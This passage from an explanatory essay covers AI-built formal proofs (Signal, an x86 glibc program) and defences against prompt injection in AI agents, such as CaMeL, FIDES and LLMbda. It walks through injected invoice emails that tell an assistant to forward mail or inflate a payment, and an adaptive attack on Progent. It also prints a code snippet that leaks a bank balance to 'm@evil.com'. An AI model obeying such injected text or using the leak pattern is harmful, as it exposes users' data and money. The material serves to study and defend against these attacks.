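Programs can also do the wrong thing without crashing. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines logic bugs as behaviour that conflicts with the implicit rules of how software should work, and notes that they rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect. A bug of this kind in the OPNsense firewall let attackers reach the user-management page, and a proof that the firewall never crashes would not have ruled it out. Assertions can add some of these rules to the theorem. If a test program compresses its input, decompresses the result and asserts that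 the output matches the original input, the theorem implies that the library never corrupts data in this way.

### Signal's encryption, down to machine code

Google DeepMind chose a more demanding kind of property for AlphaProof Code, a system of AI agents that writes specifications and proofs in Lean. *DeepMind AlphaProof Code* (Ganglani, 2026) describes it as a descendant of AlphaProof, which reached silver-medal standard at the International Mathematical Olympiad in 2024. DeepMind applied the system to libsignal, the library behind the messaging app Signal.

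Two phones that use Signal begin with a handshake called PQXDH, in which they agree on a secret key. A procedure called the Triple Ratchet then produces a new key for each message. In simplified form, each phone holds a key kᵢ and computes:

- the key for message i: mᵢ = F(kᵢ)
- the next key: kᵢ₊₁ = G(kᵢ)

The phone then deletes kᵢ and mᵢ. The functions F and G are easy to compute but infeasible to reverse, so a thief who steals k₁₀ can compute the keys that follow but not the earlier ones. Old messages stay secret, a property called forward secrecy. To protect later messages as well, the phones regularly agree on a new random secret r and mix it into the next key. A thief who has the old key but not r can't read what follows, which is called post-compromise security. The Triple Ratchet mixes in secrets from a conventional method and from one meant to resist quantum computers, so an attacker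 would have to break both.

A proof about this design doesn't show that the program follows it. A program could, for example, reuse the same r by mistake. Chaudhuri and colleagues proved forward secrecy and post-compromise security for the compiled code itself. They also proved that an attacker can't pass as one of the two parties (authentication) and that the key from the handshake stays secret. They say no one had previously connected such guarantees to the unmodified code of a widely used cryptographic protocol.

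The proofs are either symbolic or computational. A symbolic proof assumes that encryption cannot be broken without the right key, and covers every way an attacker could intercept, combine and resend messages. A computational proof treats messages as strings of bits and covers attackers who can run any efficient algorithm. It shows that their chance of success is tiny, provided certain mathematical problems are as hard as cryptographers believe.

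AlphaProof Code separates the agent that states a theorem from the agents that prove it. One agent drafts the specification with human guidance, and according to Ganglani, experts reviewed every specification before the proof work began. A team of other agents then searches for proofs without human help. The system accepts a proof only if Lean's kernel confirms that it establishes the approved specification, so the proving agents can't weaken the theorem.

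The agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof. People still have to get the 26,000 trusted lines of specifications and processor model right, and that is about three times the length of the whole seL4 kernel. But the processor model can be reused for other programs.

Chaudhuri and colleagues tested the system by putting two long-fixed bugs back into a separate copy of the code. For each version, they obtained a machine-checked proof that the code was insecure. This is stronger evidence than a failed attempt to prove it secure, since a prover may fail just because a proof is hard to find. The test also indicates that the specification is strong enough to rule out both bugs. But the team knew about these bugs in advance, so the test provides little evidence about bugs that nobody has thought of.

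AlphaProof Code found no new flaws in the parts of Signal it examined, according to a Wired report quoted in Schneier's *Formal Verification of the Signal Protocol Using AI* (2026). The proof covers a small test program for one-to-one sessions and messages, not the whole of libsignal, according to EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026). It also doesn't cover the rest of the app, including its screens and message storage. An attacker who takes over the phone can read messages there without breaking the encryption.

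### A complete x86 program

The security company Zellic and its partner V12 worked on x86 programs that use glibc, a combination that Anthropic and Theorem had left out. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents a Lean proof about one such program, covering its execution from the moment Linux starts it until it ends. Leip believes it is the first published proof of this kind.

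Even a very simple program is hard to verify in this setting. Before a C program reaches `main`, the function where the programmer's own code begins, glibc has to set up memory and choose which versions of its functions to use. This startup work executes about ten times as many distinct instructions as musl's does on RISC-V. For example, glibc compares strings with a version of `strcmp` written for recent processors that has 316 instructions and 45 jumps, while musl's RISC-V version has 14 instructions and 4 jumps.

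The theorem covers every run of the program. A run that reaches `main` must end in a specified way. The theorem also allows a run to crash or get stuck during start-up, but it limits what the run can do before then, such as what it can write to its output. A program that always crashed during start-up would satisfy this part of the theorem, but running it would reveal the crash.

The proof has several assumptions about the computer:

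- The processor is the same model as the one in the developers' virtual machine. On a different processor, glibc might choose other versions of its functions, which the proof doesn't cover.
- The kernel never refuses the program's requests for more memory.
- The vDSO, a small piece of code that Linux places in each process, is either missing or identical to the one on the test system.
- Nothing outside the process interferes with it, and nobody has changed glibc's optional settings.

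The assumption about memory is the easiest for an attacker to break, because another program on the same machine might use up the memory. If the kernel then refuses a request for more memory, the theorem no longer applies, although the program may still handle the refusal correctly.

The method currently works only for single-threaded, statically linked programs, meaning those whose files contain all the library code they use. Most Linux programs are dynamically linked and load glibc from the system when they start, so their behaviour depends on the installed version. Zellic and V12 describe their release as a research preview and plan to publish more results.

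### Memory, time and communication compared

All three projects work with machine code, where a memory error can change anything the program does afterwards. Anthropic and Theorem explicitly exclude memory errors. Ganglani says that DeepMind didn't check for crashes, and a program can crash without violating any of the four security properties. But DeepMind's proof must exclude memory errors that would let an attacker extract a key or forge a message, for the reason Chlipala gave about the shortest-path program. The Zellic and V12 theorem excludes any memory error that would make a run end in the wrong way after reaching `main`.

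Guarantees about time are weaker. If "exits normally" means that every run ends, the Anthropic and Theorem result rules out endless loops, as does the Zellic and V12 theorem for runs that reach `main`. But a program that takes a year to end would satisfy both, so a server that uses one of these programs needs a separate time limit. The four Signal properties are about secrecy and identity, so a program that never replied would not violate them.

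Only the Signal proof is about keeping secrets. The Zellic and V12 theorem limits what a program may write but does not establish noninterference. A library could satisfy the no-crash theorem and still copy a password into its output. Even the Signal properties, as cryptographers usually define them, cover the messages an attacker can see but not how long the phone takes to compute them, so ruling out timing leaks would require a separate constant-time proof.

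Keles therefore thinks people should say which properties of a piece of software have been verified instead of calling it "formally verified". People used to infer from a system's reputation that its developers had proved something nontrivial. They trusted CompCert and seL4 because the results had gone through years of peer review and other researchers had built on them. Keles guesses that AI has increased the amount of "verified" software a thousandfold, which is far too much to scrutinize in the same way.

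### Cost, and code that changes

A proof about machine code applies to one exact sequence of bytes. If a developer patches the program or compiles the same source with a newer compiler, the proof doesn't cover the new version. Even a small patch can move other functions to new addresses, which changes the instructions that call them. Users can check whether they have the verified program by comparing their file with the verified one. A phone that installs an updated version of Signal is running code that the DeepMind proof doesn't cover.

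When code changes, developers have to repeat or repair its proof, which was hardly practical when proofs took years. Wasmtime's developers left the proof of their compiler rules out of date, and a critical bug got through. Projects using AI have been faster. DeepMind's work on Signal took four weeks, and Zellic and V12 published their first results about six weeks after starting, including the time to model the processor. Chaudhuri and colleagues needed people to review only about 1% of the code.

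category.xyz's *finding bugs that frontier models miss* gives a rare figure for the same task with and without AI. Its developers had designed a rule for a blockchain under which any transaction the network accepts must be able to pay at least its gas fees when it executes. In July 2025, they spent four person-weeks proving by hand that a model of the rule works. They think AI agents could now do more than 95% of that proof. This is an estimate, not a measurement, but the 27 working days that one researcher and Claude spent on the Move borrow checker suggest savings of a similar kind.

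Repairing a proof after a patch should usually take less work than writing it from scratch, because most of the lemmas will need only small changes. An urgent security fix may still have to go out before the new proof is ready. The specification needs revising only when the program's intended behaviour changes, so people can reuse their review of it across many versions.

### Specifications as the bottleneck

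As proofs get easier to produce, more of the remaining work is in deciding what to prove. Tolmach and Klaus, whose company sells verification services, argue that specification and modelling are now the bottleneck. For example, before anyone can prove that a queue shared by several threads is correct, someone has to make decisions that the proof checker can't: whether items must come out in the order they went in, whether the program can run out of memory, and which operations other threads can interrupt.

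AI models can also write specifications, but the results so far are poor. Tolmach and Klaus describe SysMoBench, a benchmark whose developers asked Claude for a formal specification of etcd, a database that keeps copies on several computers. Claude returned essentially the textbook version of the protocol, from the appendix of the paper that introduced it. This specification passed every check but had little to do with etcd's code. In a specification of another system, ZooKeeper, a computer kept old votes that the real code overwrites. Across leading AI models, the specifications scored nearly 100% for syntax but only about 46% for agreement with the code.

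Studies of mathematical statements find the same gap. In one that Tolmach and Klaus cite, 89.5% of an agent's Lean versions of graduate-level statements passed Lean's checks, but only 60.5% had the intended meaning. Another benchmark, FaithformBench, gives models false statements to translate, such as "if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 51" (the correct value is 9 × 5 = 45). A model called Kimina translated this statement into Lean but declared x to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, so the translated statement is vacuously true, and Lean accepts a proof of it.

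A mistake in a software specification can make any program pass. For example, if no request can meet the definition of "valid", the theorem that a server handles every valid request correctly is true of every server. Developers can detect this by also requiring a proof that at least one request is valid. They can also break the program on purpose and see whether it still passes, as Fonseca and colleagues did with IronFleet and DeepMind did with Signal. Having a second model review the specification is less reliable. In a study of specifications for Rust programs, model reviewers missed a quarter of the faulty ones.

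Testing a model against the real program seems to work better. Andrews and Zhang (2026), in *Formalizing CPython*, had Claude translate parts of CPython, the program that runs most Python code, into Lean. One of the functions counts the numbers from lo up to but not including hi, in steps of a given size:

count = 1 + ⌊(hi − 1 − lo) / step⌋

With lo = 0, hi = 10 and step = 3, the count is 4, for 0, 3, 6 and 9. CPython does this arithmetic with 64-bit numbers that wrap around. The Lean version has to do the same, because a version with ordinary whole numbers would be simpler but would describe a different program.

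Andrews and Zhang ran each translated function and the original on tens of thousands of inputs before trying to prove anything. An agent that hadn't written the translation then reviewed the work. By November 2026, 4,071 functions had passed, covering about 16% of CPython. The project produced 418 bug reports, and about 55 of the bugs let ordinary Python code crash the interpreter or corrupt its memory.

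Trying to write a proof can therefore be a good way to find bugs even when the specification is doubtful. Tolmach and Klaus give another example, in which the head of Anthropic's Claude Code team had a model formalise a software library and got 16 sets of fixes from a couple of short prompts. The bugs were real, but Tolmach and Klaus don't think such a run can establish that the code is correct.

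Reusing fuzz tests avoids much of the difficulty, because nearly everyone agrees that a library shouldn't crash. Signal's security goals also have precise definitions that cryptographers have discussed for years. Much other software has no comparably clear goals. Keles compares a database to a car's engine, whose function engineers can specify exactly, and a user interface to the car's seat, whose quality depends on taste and on who is sitting in it. One can still prove particular facts about a user interface, but Keles doubts that it has any single definition of correctness.

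## AI agents that read untrusted text

Formal verification can guarantee that no email will corrupt a mail program's memory. But if the program passes the email to a language model that can make payments, the sender can ask for money in the email without corrupting any memory. An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, which are functions such as "send an email" or "make a payment" that ordinary code runs when the model requests them. Prompt injection is text placed in material that an AI system reads, which the system follows as if it were an instruction.

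Suppose an assistant has access to its user's mailbox and bank account. The user writes, "Pay the invoice that Acme emailed me." The assistant finds the email, which asks for £480 and gives an account number. Below the invoice, an attacker has added a sentence telling the assistant to forward the user's ten latest emails to another address. If the assistant does this, it uses only tools it has permission to use, and each tool works as its programmers intended.

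### Instructions and data in one string

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the loop that such agents run. Code around the model sends it the conversation so far, and the model replies with either an answer for the user or a request for a tool call. If the model requests a call, the code makes it, adds the result to the conversation and sends everything again. Each time the code sends the conversation, it joins all the messages into a single string of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes.

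Markers in the string show which parts came from the user and which from a tool. But the model computes each new token from the whole string:

P(next token | developer's instructions, user's request, email)

The email and the request are inputs to the same function, and nothing in the computation stops the email from acting as a command. Developers train models to ignore instructions in tool results, which makes attacks fail more often but doesn't rule any of them out. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites measurements showing that neither prompting nor further training reliably makes models separate instructions from data. It also quotes Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

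Databases once had the same weakness as Verdi's servers, where text from a user could end one command and begin another. Programmers solved this with parameterised queries, in which the database parses a command containing placeholders, then fills them with the user's text. This relies on a grammar that separates instructions from information, which English lacks. For example, "please pay £480 by Friday" is both an instruction and information.

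### Input that a parser can recognise

Language-theoretic security generalizes the lesson from databases. Len Sassaman, Meredith Patterson, Sergey Bratus and others argued from about 2011 that a program should define its valid inputs as a formal language and check each input in full against that definition before acting on any of it. The language should be simple enough that the check always gives an answer, as it does for regular expressions and context-free grammars. If an input can be a program in a general-purpose language, no check can always determine what it will do, because of the halting problem.

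Suppose Acme sent its invoices in this form:

```
INVOICE <6 digits> SUPPLIER <4 digits> PENCE <1 to 7 digits>
```

A parser can check such a message in one pass, and any message it accepts contains only three numbers. An attacker can choose the numbers but can't tell the program to forward emails, because no valid message has that meaning. The attacker can still send a well-formed invoice for £48,000, since the grammar can't establish that an invoice is genuine.

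People want an email assistant because it can handle messages that fit no such grammar, so it can't apply the principle to incoming email. Designers can apply a similar principle later, by controlling what passes from the untrusted text to the code that operates the tools.

### The dual-model pattern and CaMeL

In 2023 Simon Willison, who had coined the term "prompt injection", proposed dividing the work between two models. The privileged model reads the user's request and chooses the tool calls, but never receives untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary code stores the quarantined model's answers in named variables, and the privileged model refers to them by name without receiving their contents.

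In the example, the privileged model requests the amount and account number from Acme's email, then a payment of `$amount` to `$account`. Only the quarantined model reads the sentence about forwarding emails. It may return a strange answer, but it can't forward anything. It can still return the attacker's account number as `$account`, and the code will send the payment there.

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in March 2025, adds checks on the values. Its privileged model writes the plan as a Python program, as *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes, before the system reads any untrusted data. The plan for the invoice might be:

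```
email = find_email(sender="Acme")
bill = ask_quarantined(email, "amount and account")
pay(bill.account, bill.amount)
```

A special interpreter runs this program. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), the interpreter tracks where each value came from and checks a policy before every tool call. Here `bill.account` is labeled as coming from an email. If the policy for `pay` requires the account number to come from the user or the user's saved payees, the call fails the check, and the interpreter blocks it or asks the user to approve it. A better plan would look up Acme among the saved payees and take only the amount from the email.

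The labels also record who may receive a value, so a policy for sending email can stop a plan from sending the user's bank statement to Acme.

### FIDES

Some tasks don't allow a complete plan in advance. If the user says "complete the tasks due today in my to-do app", nobody can choose the tool calls without reading the list. Costa and colleagues make this distinction precise. Let S(d) be the set of action sequences that solve a task when the stored data are d. The task is data-independent if one sequence works for all possible data:

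⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅, taken over every possible d

The to-do task is data-dependent, so the agent has to learn something from the data before it can act.

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses one tool call at a time. It labels every message and tool result as trusted or untrusted, and as public or secret. The conversation's own label combines the labels of everything in it. If an untrusted email enters the conversation, the conversation becomes untrusted, and a policy can forbid payments from then on.

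FIDES stores a tool result in a variable whenever adding it to the conversation would change the conversation's label, so that the agent can still act. The model can pass the variable to another tool without seeing its contents. It can also have a quarantined model extract an answer from the variable in a fixed format, such as a whole number or a yes or no. The software allows only tokens that fit the format, so the answer, unlike the email, belongs to a simple formal language.

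An attacker who controls a yes-or-no answer can choose between only two outcomes. FIDES can therefore let such small answers pass a policy that would otherwise reject untrusted data, although its developers left this option off in their tests.

### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a 2024 benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated office, chat, travel and banking systems. Testers plant malicious text in tool results and record whether the agent completes the user's task and whether it achieves the attacker's goal.

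Narisetty and colleagues report that in 2025 CaMeL completed 77% of tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an agent without defences, and that no attack within its stated threat model succeeded. CaMeL used almost three times as many tokens.

In tests from May 2025, FIDES stopped every attack when it had suitable policies. With policy checks on, it completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more when both used o1. With the checks off, practical attacks succeeded against every design tested, including FIDES. The checks therefore provide the security, and the variables allow more tasks to pass those checks.

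How much policy checks reduce task completion depends heavily on the kind of work. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with newer models. Without attacks, CaMeL completed about 70% of the tasks with its policy checks off and 37.5% with them on. Many banking tasks require the agent to act on something it has read in a file or message, which a strict policy forbids.

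Garby and colleagues also looked at why attacks fail. The banking tests combine 16 tasks with nine attacks, giving 144 pairs. In 97 of these, the attack needs a tool call that would normally never appear in a plan for the user's task, so fixing the plan in advance is enough to stop it. Labels and policies matter mainly for the other 47. The one exception among the 97 came when CaMeL's planning model was asked to follow the instructions in a file and wrote a program that called whichever tool the file named. With the policy checks off, this let whoever had written the file choose the tool call.

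### Attackers who adapt

The AgentDojo attacks come from a fixed list, and testing against such lists has made defences look stronger than they were before. Milad Nasr and colleagues examined twelve defences that train the model to resist injections, filter its input or warn it in the prompt. For most of them, the originally reported attack success rate was near zero. Attacks designed for each defence succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

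In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues at the security company LaunchSafe tried an adaptive attack on Progent. Like CaMeL and FIDES, Progent puts its checks outside the agent's model, comparing each tool call with rules about tools and their arguments. But another model writes these rules and can loosen them after reading tool results. The researchers tried to fool that model by describing the malicious action as a routine step that the user had already authorised.

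| | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, possibly because its milder wording also made the agent less likely to obey it. The result is only weak evidence that the defence is robust. The agent used a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, and the team tried one handwritten attack on eight tasks from each of three groups. In one group, no attack worked even without a defence. The team didn't attack CaMeL or FIDES.

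A better reason to expect checks outside the model to hold up is that an attacker who completely controls the quarantined model still can't use it to call a tool. Several groups have tried to turn arguments like this into theorems.

### Noninterference for agents

For an agent, noninterference means that the content of an untrusted email should not change the agent's trusted actions. Garby and colleagues report that FIDES has a noninterference theorem for its own loop that holds for any set of tools.

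This kind of label tracking gives a weaker guarantee for secrets. Costa and colleagues show that it can enforce safety properties and "explicit secrecy", which they consider enough to stop most practical attacks. Explicit secrecy covers data that the agent copies or computes from a secret, but not implicit flows, such as a fixed message that the assistant sends Acme only when the user's balance is above £10,000.

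CaMeL also tracks the effect of conditions, but it came without a comparable theorem, and Garby and colleagues found leaks in it. One leak uses a trick that J. S. Fenton described in 1974. In simplified form:

```
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 10000: poor = False
if poor: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL updates a variable's label only when an assignment to it runs. If the balance is high, the third line runs and `poor` becomes a secret. The fourth line then doesn't change `rich`, which stays true and public, so CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, the fourth line makes `rich` false and no email goes out. The email therefore reveals whether the balance is above £10,000.

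CaMeL can also leak information when it retries a failed plan, which happens in ordinary Python code outside the interpreter. Whether a policy blocked the last attempt can depend on a secret, so each retry can reveal another bit. An attacker doesn't write CaMeL's plans, so they could use either leak only if the planning model had already gone wrong. Still, a guarantee for every plan would be much more useful than one that relies on the planner to write sensible code.

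LLMbda, which Garby and colleagues first released in February 2026, provides such a guarantee. It is a small programming language with commands for prompting a model, making a temporary copy of a conversation, clearing a conversation and running code that the model writes. Every value and conversation has a label. Programmers can build a quarantined model by copying the conversation, clearing the copy and prompting the model there. LLMbda stops a run if a step that depends on a secret would add to a public conversation, which prevents leaks like Fenton's.

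The theorem covers every program in the language. Because models choose their words partly at random, it compares probabilities. Take two starting points that differ only in inputs the observer may not learn about, and let μ(r) and ν(r) be the probabilities that the observer sees result r. They may add up to less than 1, since some runs never finish or fail a policy check. The theorem says that there are numbers ω(r), adding up to at most 1, such that:

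μ(r) ≤ ω(r) and ν(r) ≤ ω(r) for every r

If every run finishes, μ and ν each add up to 1, so both must equal ω and the observer learns nothing. If some runs fail, the statistical distance between μ and ν is at most the average of their probabilities of failing.

That allowance can be large. Suppose a program picks a random bit, gets stuck unless it matches a secret bit, and then prints it. Every run that finishes reveals the secret bit, but the program still satisfies the theorem with ω = ½ for each bit. An agent that retries failed runs on real data could therefore leak a lot. Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, instead practises on a simulated bank account until its plan works, and only then uses the real one.

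The proof uses a second way of running each program, which skips any computation as soon as its label shows that the observer may not see it. The skipping version gives the same probabilities from both starting points and finishes at least as often as the real program, so it supplies ω. Lean checked the proof. The interpreter described in the proof is also the program that calls the model, so there is no separate handwritten version that might differ from it.

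Full noninterference would prevent the assistant from paying any amount it had read in an email. LLMbda therefore has an instruction, `endorse`, that marks untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing data this way never weakens the protection of secrets. The plan's writer must still decide whether the data deserve trust. In Randori, the planning model writes the plan and must decide this before it sees any untrusted text.

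Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2, about as many as CaMeL completed with its policy checks turned off. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. With the other two models, removing `endorse` reduced the number of completed runs from 36 to 30 and from 31 to 26.

### Relative security

Dongol (November 2026) argues in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* that noninterference is the wrong standard for secrets too. Suppose a user wants an assistant to reply to meeting requests with times when the user is free. The replies depend on the user's private calendar, so an assistant that does this task violates noninterference. A declassification policy could permit the replies, but someone would have to write one for every task.

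Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent. Both follow the same plan under the same monitor, which allows or denies each tool call, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. Call two possible values of the user's secrets distinguishable if some message from the attacker makes the agent's visible actions differ between them. The agent is relatively secure if:

pairs distinguishable through the real agent ⊆ pairs distinguishable through the reference agent

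If an injected instruction makes the assistant send the calendar, the attacker learns nothing they couldn't have obtained with a genuine meeting request. But the assistant fails the test if the instruction also makes it send a password-reset code, because no message would make the reference agent reveal the code.

The definition can allow an injection to reveal much more than the reference agent does. Suppose the reference agent tells anyone whether a guessed password is correct. Guessing one of any two passwords is enough to tell them apart, so the definition counts an injection that reveals the entire password as secure. Dongol gives a stricter version that excludes this case by fixing the reference agent's input without regard to the secret.

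The main theorem concerns a "fence", a monitor that permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted text. With a fence, every plan is relatively secure against an attacker who sees the contents and order of the agent's messages but not their timing. The proof assumes that each injection causes a single tool call and that when the model obeys an injection doesn't depend on secrets. An assistant that only summarises invoices can still do its job behind a fence, but one that has to pay an invoice after reading it can't if the fence covers payments.

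Dongol used the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL to prove or refute the security of 25 small example agents. They include these designs:

| Design | Verdict |
|---|---|
| Withdraw the sending tool before reading the email | Secure |
| Withdraw it after reading the email | Leaks |
| User approves one use of the sending tool, with any content | Leaks |
| User approves the exact message | Secure if the attacker can't observe timing |
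| Limit of one message, which the plan sends before reading the email | Secure |
| Limit of one message, which the plan sends after reading the email | Leaks |
| Mark untrusted text and tell the model not to obey it | Leaks unless the model respects the marks |
| Dual model without labels | Leaks |
| Dual model with labels on data | Secure if refusals are invisible, but also blocks the honest reply |
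| Same, with a plan that branches on the quarantined model's answer | Leaks |

The two results about approval show how much such details matter. If the user approves "one email", an injected instruction can use up the approval to send private data before the planned email goes out. If the user approves an exact message, an injected message gets through only if it is identical. An identical message still arrives a step early, so an attacker who can measure timing learns that the private data matched the approved text.

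In the last design in the table, the quarantined model can read the user's notes, and the plan sends 1 or 0 depending on the model's answer. Both numbers are public, so they pass the label check, but the choice between them can reveal something about the notes. This example represents CaMeL's normal mode. Dongol didn't model CaMeL's strict mode, which is meant to prevent this leak.

These verdicts apply to simplified agents, and some of the "secure" verdicts cover only a particular attack. The definition covers only leaks, so a fraudulent payment that reveals no secret doesn't violate it. The definition also requires a plan fixed in advance, which excludes agents whose model chooses every call. A monitor that denied every call would satisfy the definition, so developers have to test separately whether the agent is still useful.

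### Agents with lasting memory

An injection has more time to take effect when an agent remembers its earlier work. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, August 2026) uses an example much like the one here. On Monday, the user asks the agent to find Acme's invoice and keep the details. On Tuesday, the user asks it to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the agent copies Monday's text into Tuesday's conversation, it also copies any malicious instruction in that text. Even without such an instruction, the stored account number may be the attacker's.

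SPA, their system, stores three things for each result: the value, its label and a description of what the value represents. On Tuesday the planning model sees only the description. It writes a complete plan that retrieves the invoice by reference, and the value comes back with Monday's label. Before any tool runs, a checker goes through the plan and allows data to pass from a source to a destination only if:

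secrecy(source) ≤ secrecy(destination) and trust(source) ≥ trust(destination)

When the destination is a tool, its secrecy level is the highest level of secrecy its inputs may have, and its trust level is the lowest level of trust they may have. If `pay` requires trusted inputs, the checker rejects a plan that takes the account number from the untrusted invoice. It also rejects "if the invoice is overdue, pay Acme £480", because whether the payment happens depends on untrusted data.

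Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on a version they made by splitting each task into several requests. The figures below are for plans that use the installed tools directly:

| | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Single requests, no label checks | 0.4% | 53.0% |
| Single requests, label checks | 0.0% | 29.0% |
| Several requests, no label checks | 0.3% | 62.5% |
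| Several requests, label checks | 0.2% | 35.3% |

The label checks reduced the number of completed tasks by nearly half and stopped only a few attacks, because planning in advance had already stopped most of them. The tests also provide little evidence about the memory design, since attackers still succeeded only 0.6% of the time when Girrens and Wang showed the planning model the stored values directly. They acknowledge that AgentDojo's attacks weren't designed to lie dormant until a later request. The case for SPA's memory design therefore rests mainly on the argument that text the planner never sees can't change the plan.

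Other agents can pass on an injection in a similar way. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* considers an attack in which an injection planted in a database spreads from one agent to another.

### Proofs about permissions

All these systems enforce policies that someone has to write, and individually sensible rules can combine badly. Suppose the invoice assistant has these permissions:

- It may read email.
- It may pay any account on the list of saved payees.
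- It may update that list, so that suppliers' details stay correct.

The user wants to be sure that money goes only to accounts they have approved. But an agent under an attacker's control could read an account number in an email, add it to the list of approved accounts and pay it, without breaking any of the rules.

A permission prover looks for such combinations automatically. It translates the rules into logic and uses a solver to check whether any permitted sequence of actions leads to a forbidden result. If there is one, the solver returns it as an example. If every change to the list requires the user's approval, no such sequence exists, and the solver can prove it. Amazon has for years used a related tool, Zelkova, to analyse access policies in its cloud service, and NVIDIA has developed a prover for AI agents' permissions.

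A proof of this kind needs no assumptions about how the language model behaves, so it holds even if an attacker controls the agent completely. It does depend on a sandbox that enforces the rules and on an accurate description of what each tool can do. If the payment tool also fetches web addresses it is given, and the description leaves this out, the agent can send out data in a way the proof doesn't cover.

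### The forged invoice

Suppose the assistant now has a fixed plan, takes Acme's account number from the saved payees, and endorses the amount it finds in the email. The user has also asked for a summary of the email. The outcome depends on what the attacker writes:

| Content of the email | Outcome |
|---|---|
| An instruction to forward the user's mail | Nothing happens, because the plan doesn't include that call |
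| The attacker's account number | The money still goes to Acme's saved account |
| An amount of £4,800 instead of £480 | The assistant pays £4,800 |
| A false claim that Acme will cut off service tomorrow | The claim appears in the summary |

The system controls which tools run and where the money and data may go, but it doesn't check whether the email is true. The third case breaks no rules, because the user asked the assistant to make the payment described in the invoice. In the two successful attacks on Randori, the user had similarly asked it to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without `endorse`, Randori blocked these attacks, but it could no longer carry out the task when the file was genuine.

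Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's developers found the same case and placed it outside their threat model. They regard such attacks as the limit of what any system based on information flow can stop. Narisetty and colleagues call tasks in which untrusted text has to determine an important action the deepest open problem in the field. The usual answer is to ask the user for approval, but people who see many such requests tend to approve them without reading them. These defences don't address false summaries, which do harm when a person believes them.

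The labels can also be wrong from the start. These systems treat what the user types as trusted, so a user who pastes the attacker's email into the request gives that email the user's authority. Narisetty and colleagues note that FIDES, as deployed, treats data as trusted if a programmer forgets to label it.

To guard against a wrong amount, a developer can add a rule that doesn't rely on the email. If paying more than £500 for an invoice requires approval, a forged invoice can cost at most £500 without it, though ten could cost £5,000 unless the total is also limited. If the user keeps a trusted record of orders, the plan can take the amount from there and pay only when the invoice matches. The attacker can then still trigger or prevent the payment for that order, but can't change the amount.

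## Accepting an AI's output only with a proof

Fixed plans and labels restrict what an AI agent can do, whatever its model writes. A stricter approach is to refuse a model's output unless it comes with a proof that it meets the receiver's requirements. *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) proposed this approach for programs that users want to install in an operating-system kernel, and called it proof-carrying code. The kernel's designers publish a safety policy, and the program's author attaches a proof that the program obeys it. The kernel checks the proof once before running the program, so the program can come from an unknown or untrusted author.

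### Proof-carrying code

In Necula and Lee's first example, a kernel keeps a table with an entry for each user process. Each entry has a tag at address a and a data word at a + 8. A user's code may read both words of its own entry, but it may change the data only if the tag isn't zero. The example program adds 1 to the data if the tag isn't zero. It finds the tag by subtracting 8 from the data's address, a roundabout method that Necula and Lee use to show that optimised code doesn't prevent a proof.

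The kernel works backwards through the machine code and collects the conditions that make every memory access legal. For this program, they are:

read(a + 8) ∧ read(a + 8 − 8) ∧ (M[a + 8 − 8] ≠ 0 ⇒ write(a + 8))

Here M[x] is the content of address x, and "read" and "write" mean that the policy permits the access. The author's proof must derive this formula from the policy. One step shows that a + 8 − 8 = a, which holds on a 64-bit machine if a is a valid 64-bit number. Checking the proof took 1.4 milliseconds.

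Tampering with the program doesn't help an attacker, because the kernel computes the formula from the code it received. The kernel rejects the altered program unless the proof is still valid for that formula, and a valid proof means the altered program obeys the policy too.

The main experiment used packet filters, small programs that look at each incoming network packet and decide whether an application wants it. The policy let a filter read the packet, use 16 bytes of scratch memory and jump only forwards, so every filter had to end. Necula and Lee wrote four filters in assembly language:

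| Packets the filter accepts | Instructions | Size with proof | Time to check |
|---|---|---|---|
| All internet (IP) packets | 8 | 385 bytes | 0.78 ms |
| IP packets from one network | 15 | 516 bytes | 1.07 ms |
| IP or address-lookup packets between two networks | 47 | 1,024 bytes | 2.35 ms |
| TCP packets to one port | 28 | 814 bytes | 1.71 ms |

The standard system at the time, BPF (the ancestor of eBPF), interpreted each filter and checked its memory accesses as it ran. BPF filters were about ten times slower than those accepted with a proof. For the last filter in the table, the faster execution made up for the proof-checking time after 1,200 packets, or little more than a second of the recorded network traffic. Compared with software fault isolation, which adds only a few instructions, making up that time took 28,000 packets.

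Producing the proofs was harder than checking them. A simple theorem prover took 5 to 10 seconds per filter, and sometimes a person had to add a new fact about arithmetic to it. For a routine with a loop, Necula and Lee had to write by hand the condition that stays true on every pass.

### What the packet-filter proofs left out

The policy did not restrict which packets a filter accepted, so a filter that rejected every packet or accepted the wrong ones would have passed.

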